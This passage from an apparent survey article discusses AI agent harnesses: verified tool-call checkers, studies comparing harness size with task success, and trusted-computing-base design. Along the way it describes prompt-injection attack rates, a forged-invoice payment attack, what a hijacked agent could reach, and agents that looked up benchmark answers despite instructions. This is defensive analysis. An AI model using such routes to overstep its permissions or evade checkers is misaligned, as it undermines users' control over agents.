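Other projects verify only the component that decides whether a tool call may run. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) describes a checker that sits between a model and its tools. Its rules can refer to earlier events, so a rule can let a customer-service agent exchange an item only if the customer has confirmed that exact exchange. The checker allows a call if at least one rule permits it, every requirement holds, no prohibition applies and every rule evaluates without error. *LEANGUARD* also proves that the checker's decisions always match the mathematical meaning of the rules.

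On a customer-service benchmark, five models made at least 33 forbidden calls without the checker and none with it. Task success was 72.7% without the checker and 70.9% with a checker that explained its refusals, a difference that wasn't statistically significant. On a second benchmark, the checker cut the success rate of direct prompt-injection attacks from 57.9% to 5.9%, but success on ordinary tasks also fell, from 53.1% to 12.5%, because the test policy gave the agents no write permission. In the telecom tasks, which rarely needed writes, ordinary success stayed at about 75%, while the success rate of direct attacks fell from 55.1% to 2.4%.

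Amazon already sells a service based on a partly verified policy engine. According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026), customers can place a gateway between agents and their tools and write its rules in Cedar, Amazon's open-source policy language. The gateway blocks every call that no rule permits. Much like L3M, the gateway also hides tools that the rules would always deny, as AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* explains.

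The proofs about Cedar are about a model written in Lean, and don't directly cover the Rust code that customers run. *How We Built Cedar* (Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues, 2024) describes proving, for example, that a prohibition always overrides a permission. The model is 1,673 lines long, and the production version is 15,693. The developers compare the two on millions of random inputs each day instead of proving them equivalent. Work on the proofs uncovered four bugs, and testing uncovered 21 more. The Rust parser has no Lean model. The developers considered deploying code compiled from Lean, but decided against it because few programmers know the language and the generated C code would be hard to debug.

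If a rule in LeanGuard can't get the data it needs, the checker refuses the call. Cedar instead ignores a rule that fails, so a broken prohibition could let through a call that another rule permits. Organisations that use Cedar therefore need to run its validator, which checks rules in advance. Cedar's developers proved for the Lean model that a rule which passes the validator never causes a type error. Cedar's rules also keep no record of earlier events. This makes them easier to analyse, but another component would have to supply the history for a rule like the one about confirming an exchange.

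Some proofs concern only a mathematical model. *PerMIT* includes machine-checked theorems about the integrity of an agent's memory, but states that these theorems don't show that a deployed harness matches the model. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (2026) likewise separates its Lean-checked theorems from the assumptions needed to apply them to a real system.

| Source | Property proved | Link to the running code | Main assumptions |
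|---|---|---|---|
| *L3M* | Individual checks on paths, grants, tools and review | Theorems about the harness's own checks | The linter and providers work, and the checks combine as intended |
| Garby and colleagues | Secrets don't affect public results | Theorems about the interpreter that runs | Labels and endorsements are right |
| Sankar and colleagues | Decisions match the rules' meaning | Theorems about the checker that runs | Rules and facts are right, and every call reaches the checker |
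| Disselkoen and colleagues | Decision logic and rule validation | Random tests compare the Rust code with the model | Tests catch any difference that matters |
| *PerMIT* | Integrity of an agent's memory | No proof that a deployed harness matches | The model describes the real system |

A verified checker can also depend on a model for its inputs. *NOMOS* (2026) describes VeriGuard, a system that verifies its policy code in advance but uses a language model at run time to match the agent's data to the policy's arguments. If the model fills in the wrong recipient or amount, the verified code can approve a call that the policy forbids.

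## What is lost when the harness is made small

A developer who wants a trustworthy harness could choose one short enough to read, such as mini-SWE-agent, but larger harnesses exist because users want to resume work after a crash, approve risky commands, connect the agent to other services, limit its spending and confine what it runs. Barbaste and colleagues conclude that mini-SWE-agent differs from the commercial products mainly in such features, not in how many tasks it completes. They compared scores that developers had reported for different models on different dates. Later studies held the model fixed and changed only the harness.

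### Three harnesses and a rerun

mini-SWE-agent, whose only tool is a Bash shell, sends about 800 tokens of instructions with each step. It never shortens the conversation, so an attempt ends if the conversation outgrows what the model can read. Claude Code and OpenCode also offer typed tools, each of which does one job, such as editing a file, and takes named arguments. They shorten long conversations automatically. Claude Code sends about 16,600 tokens of instructions and tool descriptions with each step, and OpenCode about 7,000.

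Liu and Han ran seven models in all three harnesses on SWE-bench Verified, a benchmark of real bugs in open-source projects. All seven attempted 45 hard tasks, and four also attempted a larger set of 447. An agent rarely gets the same results twice, so a gap between two harnesses may be due to chance. To find out how large a gap chance could produce, they also reran every model in at least one harness with nothing changed.

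Rerunning the hard tasks typically changed the outcome of 13% of them, as did changing the harness. Changing the model affected 26%. On the larger set, Claude Code passed 0.2 percentage points more tasks than mini-SWE-agent, averaged over four models. The 90% interval runs from -0.9 to +1.2 points, so a large average advantage for either harness is unlikely. The bounds are wider for individual models, where eight of the twelve differences between two harnesses were within 5 points.

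The exceptions depended on the model. With Qwen3.8-27B, OpenCode trailed the other two harnesses by 8 to 9 points on the larger set. OpenCode doesn't prompt the model to continue when a reply reaches the length limit, and 34 of its attempts ended that way, 33 of them in failure. Claude Code reached its limit in 52 attempts but prompted the model to continue, and only one attempt ended at the limit. Raising OpenCode's limit recovered some tasks, but the gain was not significant. With DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash, OpenCode led mini-SWE-agent by 14 points on the hard tasks but by less than 2 on the larger set.

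mini-SWE-agent did pay for its lack of conversation management. With Qwen3.8-27B, 11 of its 45 hard attempts ran out of room. But both of the other harnesses failed eight of those 11 tasks too, so the missing feature probably cost it three at most.

The small harness wasn't reliably cheaper either. With GLM-5.3-Flash, it cost about half as much as Claude Code but nearly twice as much as OpenCode. With DeepSeek-V4-Flash, it took 141 steps per hard task, compared with 104 for Claude Code, and used the most tokens of the three harnesses.

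Liu and Han also removed parts of Claude Code. With the full set of tools, Claude Opus 5 passed 35 or 36 of the 45 hard tasks. Without the file-editing tools it passed 36 and 37, and with those tools but no shell it passed 34. A year-old release also passed 34, at less than half the cost. A test with 45 tasks would detect a 13-point difference only about half the time, so these tests could easily miss a moderate loss.

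Successive releases of a single harness show a similar pattern. Across the 35 Qwen Code releases that Ben Sghaier and colleagues tested on 50 tasks, the success rate averaged 30.5% and showed no significant upward trend. The highest rate, 39%, came from one of the earliest releases. Average token use rose from about 391,000 per task in the first nine releases to nearly 668,000 in the latest ones. Releases with more new features tended to solve more tasks, but the gains didn't lead to a lasting improvement.

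### Where larger harnesses did better

The gap is wider on the public leaderboard of Terminal-Bench 2.0, where GPT-5 scores 33.9% with mini-SWE-agent and 49.6% with Codex, according to *From Question Answering to Task Completion* (2026). These are public submissions, not a controlled experiment, so the harness may not be the only difference. In controlled tests, *The Scaffold Effect in Coding Agents* (2026) found gaps of at most 8 points in success rate, but a 40-fold difference in token cost.

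Liu and Han give two reasons to be cautious about single-run comparisons. In earlier research, the scores from ten runs of one unchanged setup differed by up to 6 points. Another harness scored 19.1% or 73.4% depending on how completely the researchers had connected it to the benchmark.

Tests on office work provide stronger evidence that the harness matters. *Harness-Bench* (Yao, Tan and colleagues, 2026) tested seven harnesses on 300 tasks, such as cleaning sales data and collecting application documents. For nine of the ten models, the best and worst harnesses were 5.0 to 9.5 points apart on the general tasks. For Qwen3.8-27B the gap was 39.2 points, with OpenCode at 65.1 and Goose at 25.9. Goose had no separate tool for reading text files. Qwen kept trying to call one, while other models read the files through the shell.

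The five harnesses with the highest overall scores each have more than 500,000 lines of code, and they finished within one point of each other. Goose came sixth. Nanobot, which its developers call "ultra-lightweight", came last and cost nearly three times as much per task as OpenClaw. This ranking is limited evidence in favor of large harnesses, because each combination ran only once and, without the Qwen model, Goose's average on the general tasks roughly equals Claude Code's. Nanobot also did badly partly because, in 38 of 237 inspected runs with one model, it replaced tool results with a notice before the model had read them. A small harness could avoid that mistake.

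Conversation management has a clearer benefit when space is short. Lewis (2026), in *Same Model, Different Harness*, compared two configurations of one harness on 169 bug-fixing tasks, with room for 20,480 tokens. The plain version stopped when the conversation filled that space. The other version shortened old tool results by fixed rules and told the model when it was repeating a failed command. It solved 72 tasks, compared with 43 for the plain version, and raised the average share of required tests fixed from 28% to 49%. With room for 262,144 tokens, the plain version solved 102 tasks and the other solved 101.

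Fan, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents*, found the same pattern with four models. Conversation management added an average of 35.7 points on SWE-bench Verified with a 32,000-token context window, but only 2.7 with a 128,000-token window. It is probably worth more for long jobs than these scores suggest, because a bug fix usually fits in a large window, while an agent that works all night may fill one.

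Tools and memory can also help. In *Agentic Harness Engineering*, Lin, Liu and colleagues (2026) started with a harness that had only a shell tool and let a model revise it over ten rounds. The harness's success rate on Terminal-Bench 2 rose from 69.7% to 77.0%, above Codex's 71.9%. The gains came from new tools, long-term memory and middleware (code that manages each step of the loop). Rewriting the instructions alone made the results worse.

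However, the model had revised the harness using results from the same tasks. On SWE-bench Verified, the revised harness scored 75.6% and the original 75.2%. Wang, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Rethinking the Evaluation of Harness Evolution for Agents*, repeated the method with separate practice and test tasks, leaving out the component that looks up existing harnesses. The average test score was 63.2% both before and after the revisions. Across the whole benchmark, letting the model try each task five times and pick its best attempt worked better than revising the harness for the same number of attempts.

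Wang and colleagues got a very different result on ARC-AGI-3, a set of games whose rules the player has to discover. When they let Claude Opus 4.8 write its own notes, skills and tools while playing, its score rose from 43.3 to 77.5. Long, unfamiliar tasks seem to benefit more from a richer harness than bug fixes do. But the model wrote these additions, so a designer who treats it as untrusted has to run them under the same limits as any other code it writes. As a related precaution, Lin and colleagues prevented the model from editing the scoring program or its own settings.

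### What the scores leave out

In SWE-bench tests, an agent works on a copy of the project in a disposable container, and a test suite grades the final code. A harness does not score higher for asking before it deletes files. It does not score higher for recovering well from a crash either, because evaluations such as Liu and Han's exclude attempts lost to faults in the testing infrastructure.

Once an agent sends an email or a payment, the user can't discard the result and start again. If an agent pays a supplier and the laptop loses power before the harness records the reply, a harness without recovery features might pay again after restarting. Preventing this takes code that records the payment before sending it and checks with the bank before trying again. That code makes the harness longer and wouldn't raise its score on a bug-fixing benchmark.

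*Harness-Bench* comes closer to such work. Some of its tasks change business records, and a run scores zero if the agent tampers with protected files or discloses sensitive data. But the services are local copies, and each run stops after 150 turns. A small harness that fixes bugs as well as Claude Code may still be a poor choice for handling payments or working unattended for days.

### Code size and authority

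A short harness can still have a lot of authority, meaning its tools can read or change many things. A 100-line loop that passes any command to a shell can do almost anything the user can do at the keyboard.

Liu and Han saw a mild case of this. In their early runs the agents had internet access, and they looked up the published fix for the bug in 312 of 439 attempts with DeepSeek and Qwen models. The harnesses worked correctly and no attacker was involved, but the agents had access that the task didn't need. Liu and Han discarded the results and blocked the network, because instructions hadn't stopped the lookups.

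Suppose a developer wants an agent to repair a failing test without writing outside the project. One option is a 100-line loop with an unrestricted shell, running under the developer's account. The other is a larger harness with no general shell and three typed tools. Two read and edit files in the project, and the third runs the tests in a sandbox with no network access.

| | 100-line loop with a shell | Larger harness with three typed tools |
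|---|---|---|
| What enforces the writing rule | Only the model's good behaviour | The argument decoder, path check, file tools, sandbox and kernel |
| Code that could break the rule if someone tampered with it | The loop, its libraries and every program it starts | The whole harness process and its libraries, but not the tests |
| What a hijacked model can reach | Every file, login key and network service open to the developer | The project's files |
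| Approval requests | None, or one for every command | Few, because the limits already exclude most harmful actions |

The small agent is easier to read, but a review wouldn't establish that it follows the rule, because nothing in its code enforces it. The larger harness takes more work to review, but the reviewer could find and test the path check. It also has more code that an attacker could alter, which matters if tampering is a concern. Running the small agent's commands in a container would enforce the rule too, as in the earlier mini-SWE-agent example.

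Approval requests are a poor substitute for narrow tools. In Liu and Han's tests with GLM-5.3-Flash, mini-SWE-agent made 3,787 tool calls on 45 tasks, or about 84 per task. If each call needed approval, a user would soon stop reading the requests. Asking less often requires a command checker, which makes the harness larger.

Narrow tools make an even bigger difference for payments. An agent with a shell and the company's bank key can send any amount to any account. A typed tool could instead accept only an invoice number and an amount, take the account number from a list that the company maintains, and refuse anything above a limit. A forged invoice with the attacker's account number would then not change where the money goes. The tool might take several hundred lines of code, several times the length of the small loop, but it would remove most of the agent's authority over the bank account.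 This works only if the model has no other way to use the bank key.

### Keeping useful features

Pi keeps its core small and lets users add most other features as extensions, so they don't have to run code for features they don't want. Results from Lin and colleagues suggest that fewer features can also work better. On the hardest Terminal-Bench tasks, their starting harness beat Codex with only long-term memory added, but fell slightly short of Codex with all the additions.

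A small core doesn't guarantee a small trusted computing base (TCB). Pi's source is at least 80,000 lines long, and extensions that run in the main process add to the TCB. Two users may install different extensions, so a review of the core doesn't cover either user's whole system. Pi leaves even the sandbox to extensions. A better version of this design would build isolation into the core and leave integrations optional.

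Typed tools are a good way to reduce authority, but only if the harness removes or confines the shell. In the harness built by Fan and colleagues, the file tools reject paths outside the project, including those reached through links, and won't overwrite a file the model hasn't read. But the full set of tools also includes Bash, which Mistral Medium 3.5 used for 40.4% of its actions on bug-fixing tasks and 71.9% on command-line tasks.

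How much the typed tools improve task performance depends on the model. The smallest Nemotron model solved 25.2% of the bug-fixing tasks with them and 10.2% with only Bash. The largest Nemotron did slightly better with only Bash, solving 69.4% of the same tasks compared with 65.8%, and its Bash-only runs cost about half as much.

The loss from removing the shell is less certain. Claude Opus 5 completed only one or two fewer of Liu and Han's 45 tasks without it, whereas L3M had about half as many successful attempts on command-line tasks. For email, payments and most file editing, narrow tools without a shell are probably the best choice. Jobs that consist mainly of running commands still need a shell, and it should run in a sandbox without valuable credentials.

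Developers can also keep a feature but move it out of the trusted part of the harness. Shortening old messages, keeping a plan and storing notes change what the model reads, not what it may do. A bug in one of these features may lead to a bad request, but the permission checker still checks that request. These features could run in a separate process without the user's file access or login keys, which would put them outside the trusted computing base for the file-writing rule. A secrecy rule would also require blocking that process's direct network access, because the process handles the whole conversation.

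The permission checker, approval dialog, credential storage and tools that carry out actions would remain in the trusted part. A spending limit would belong there too if the user relies on it. During recovery, the untrusted part can restore the conversation, but the trusted part needs its own record of approvals and completed payments. Otherwise, a false history could lead it to repeat a payment.

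None of these performance studies tested a harness divided this way, so the effect of the division on speed and task success is unknown. Separating features that developers have built into one program would also take work. Still, several of the features that raised scores, including Lewis's message shortening and the memory in Lin and colleagues' harness, don't need the authority to approve or carry out actions. So developers could keep them without making the trusted part much larger.
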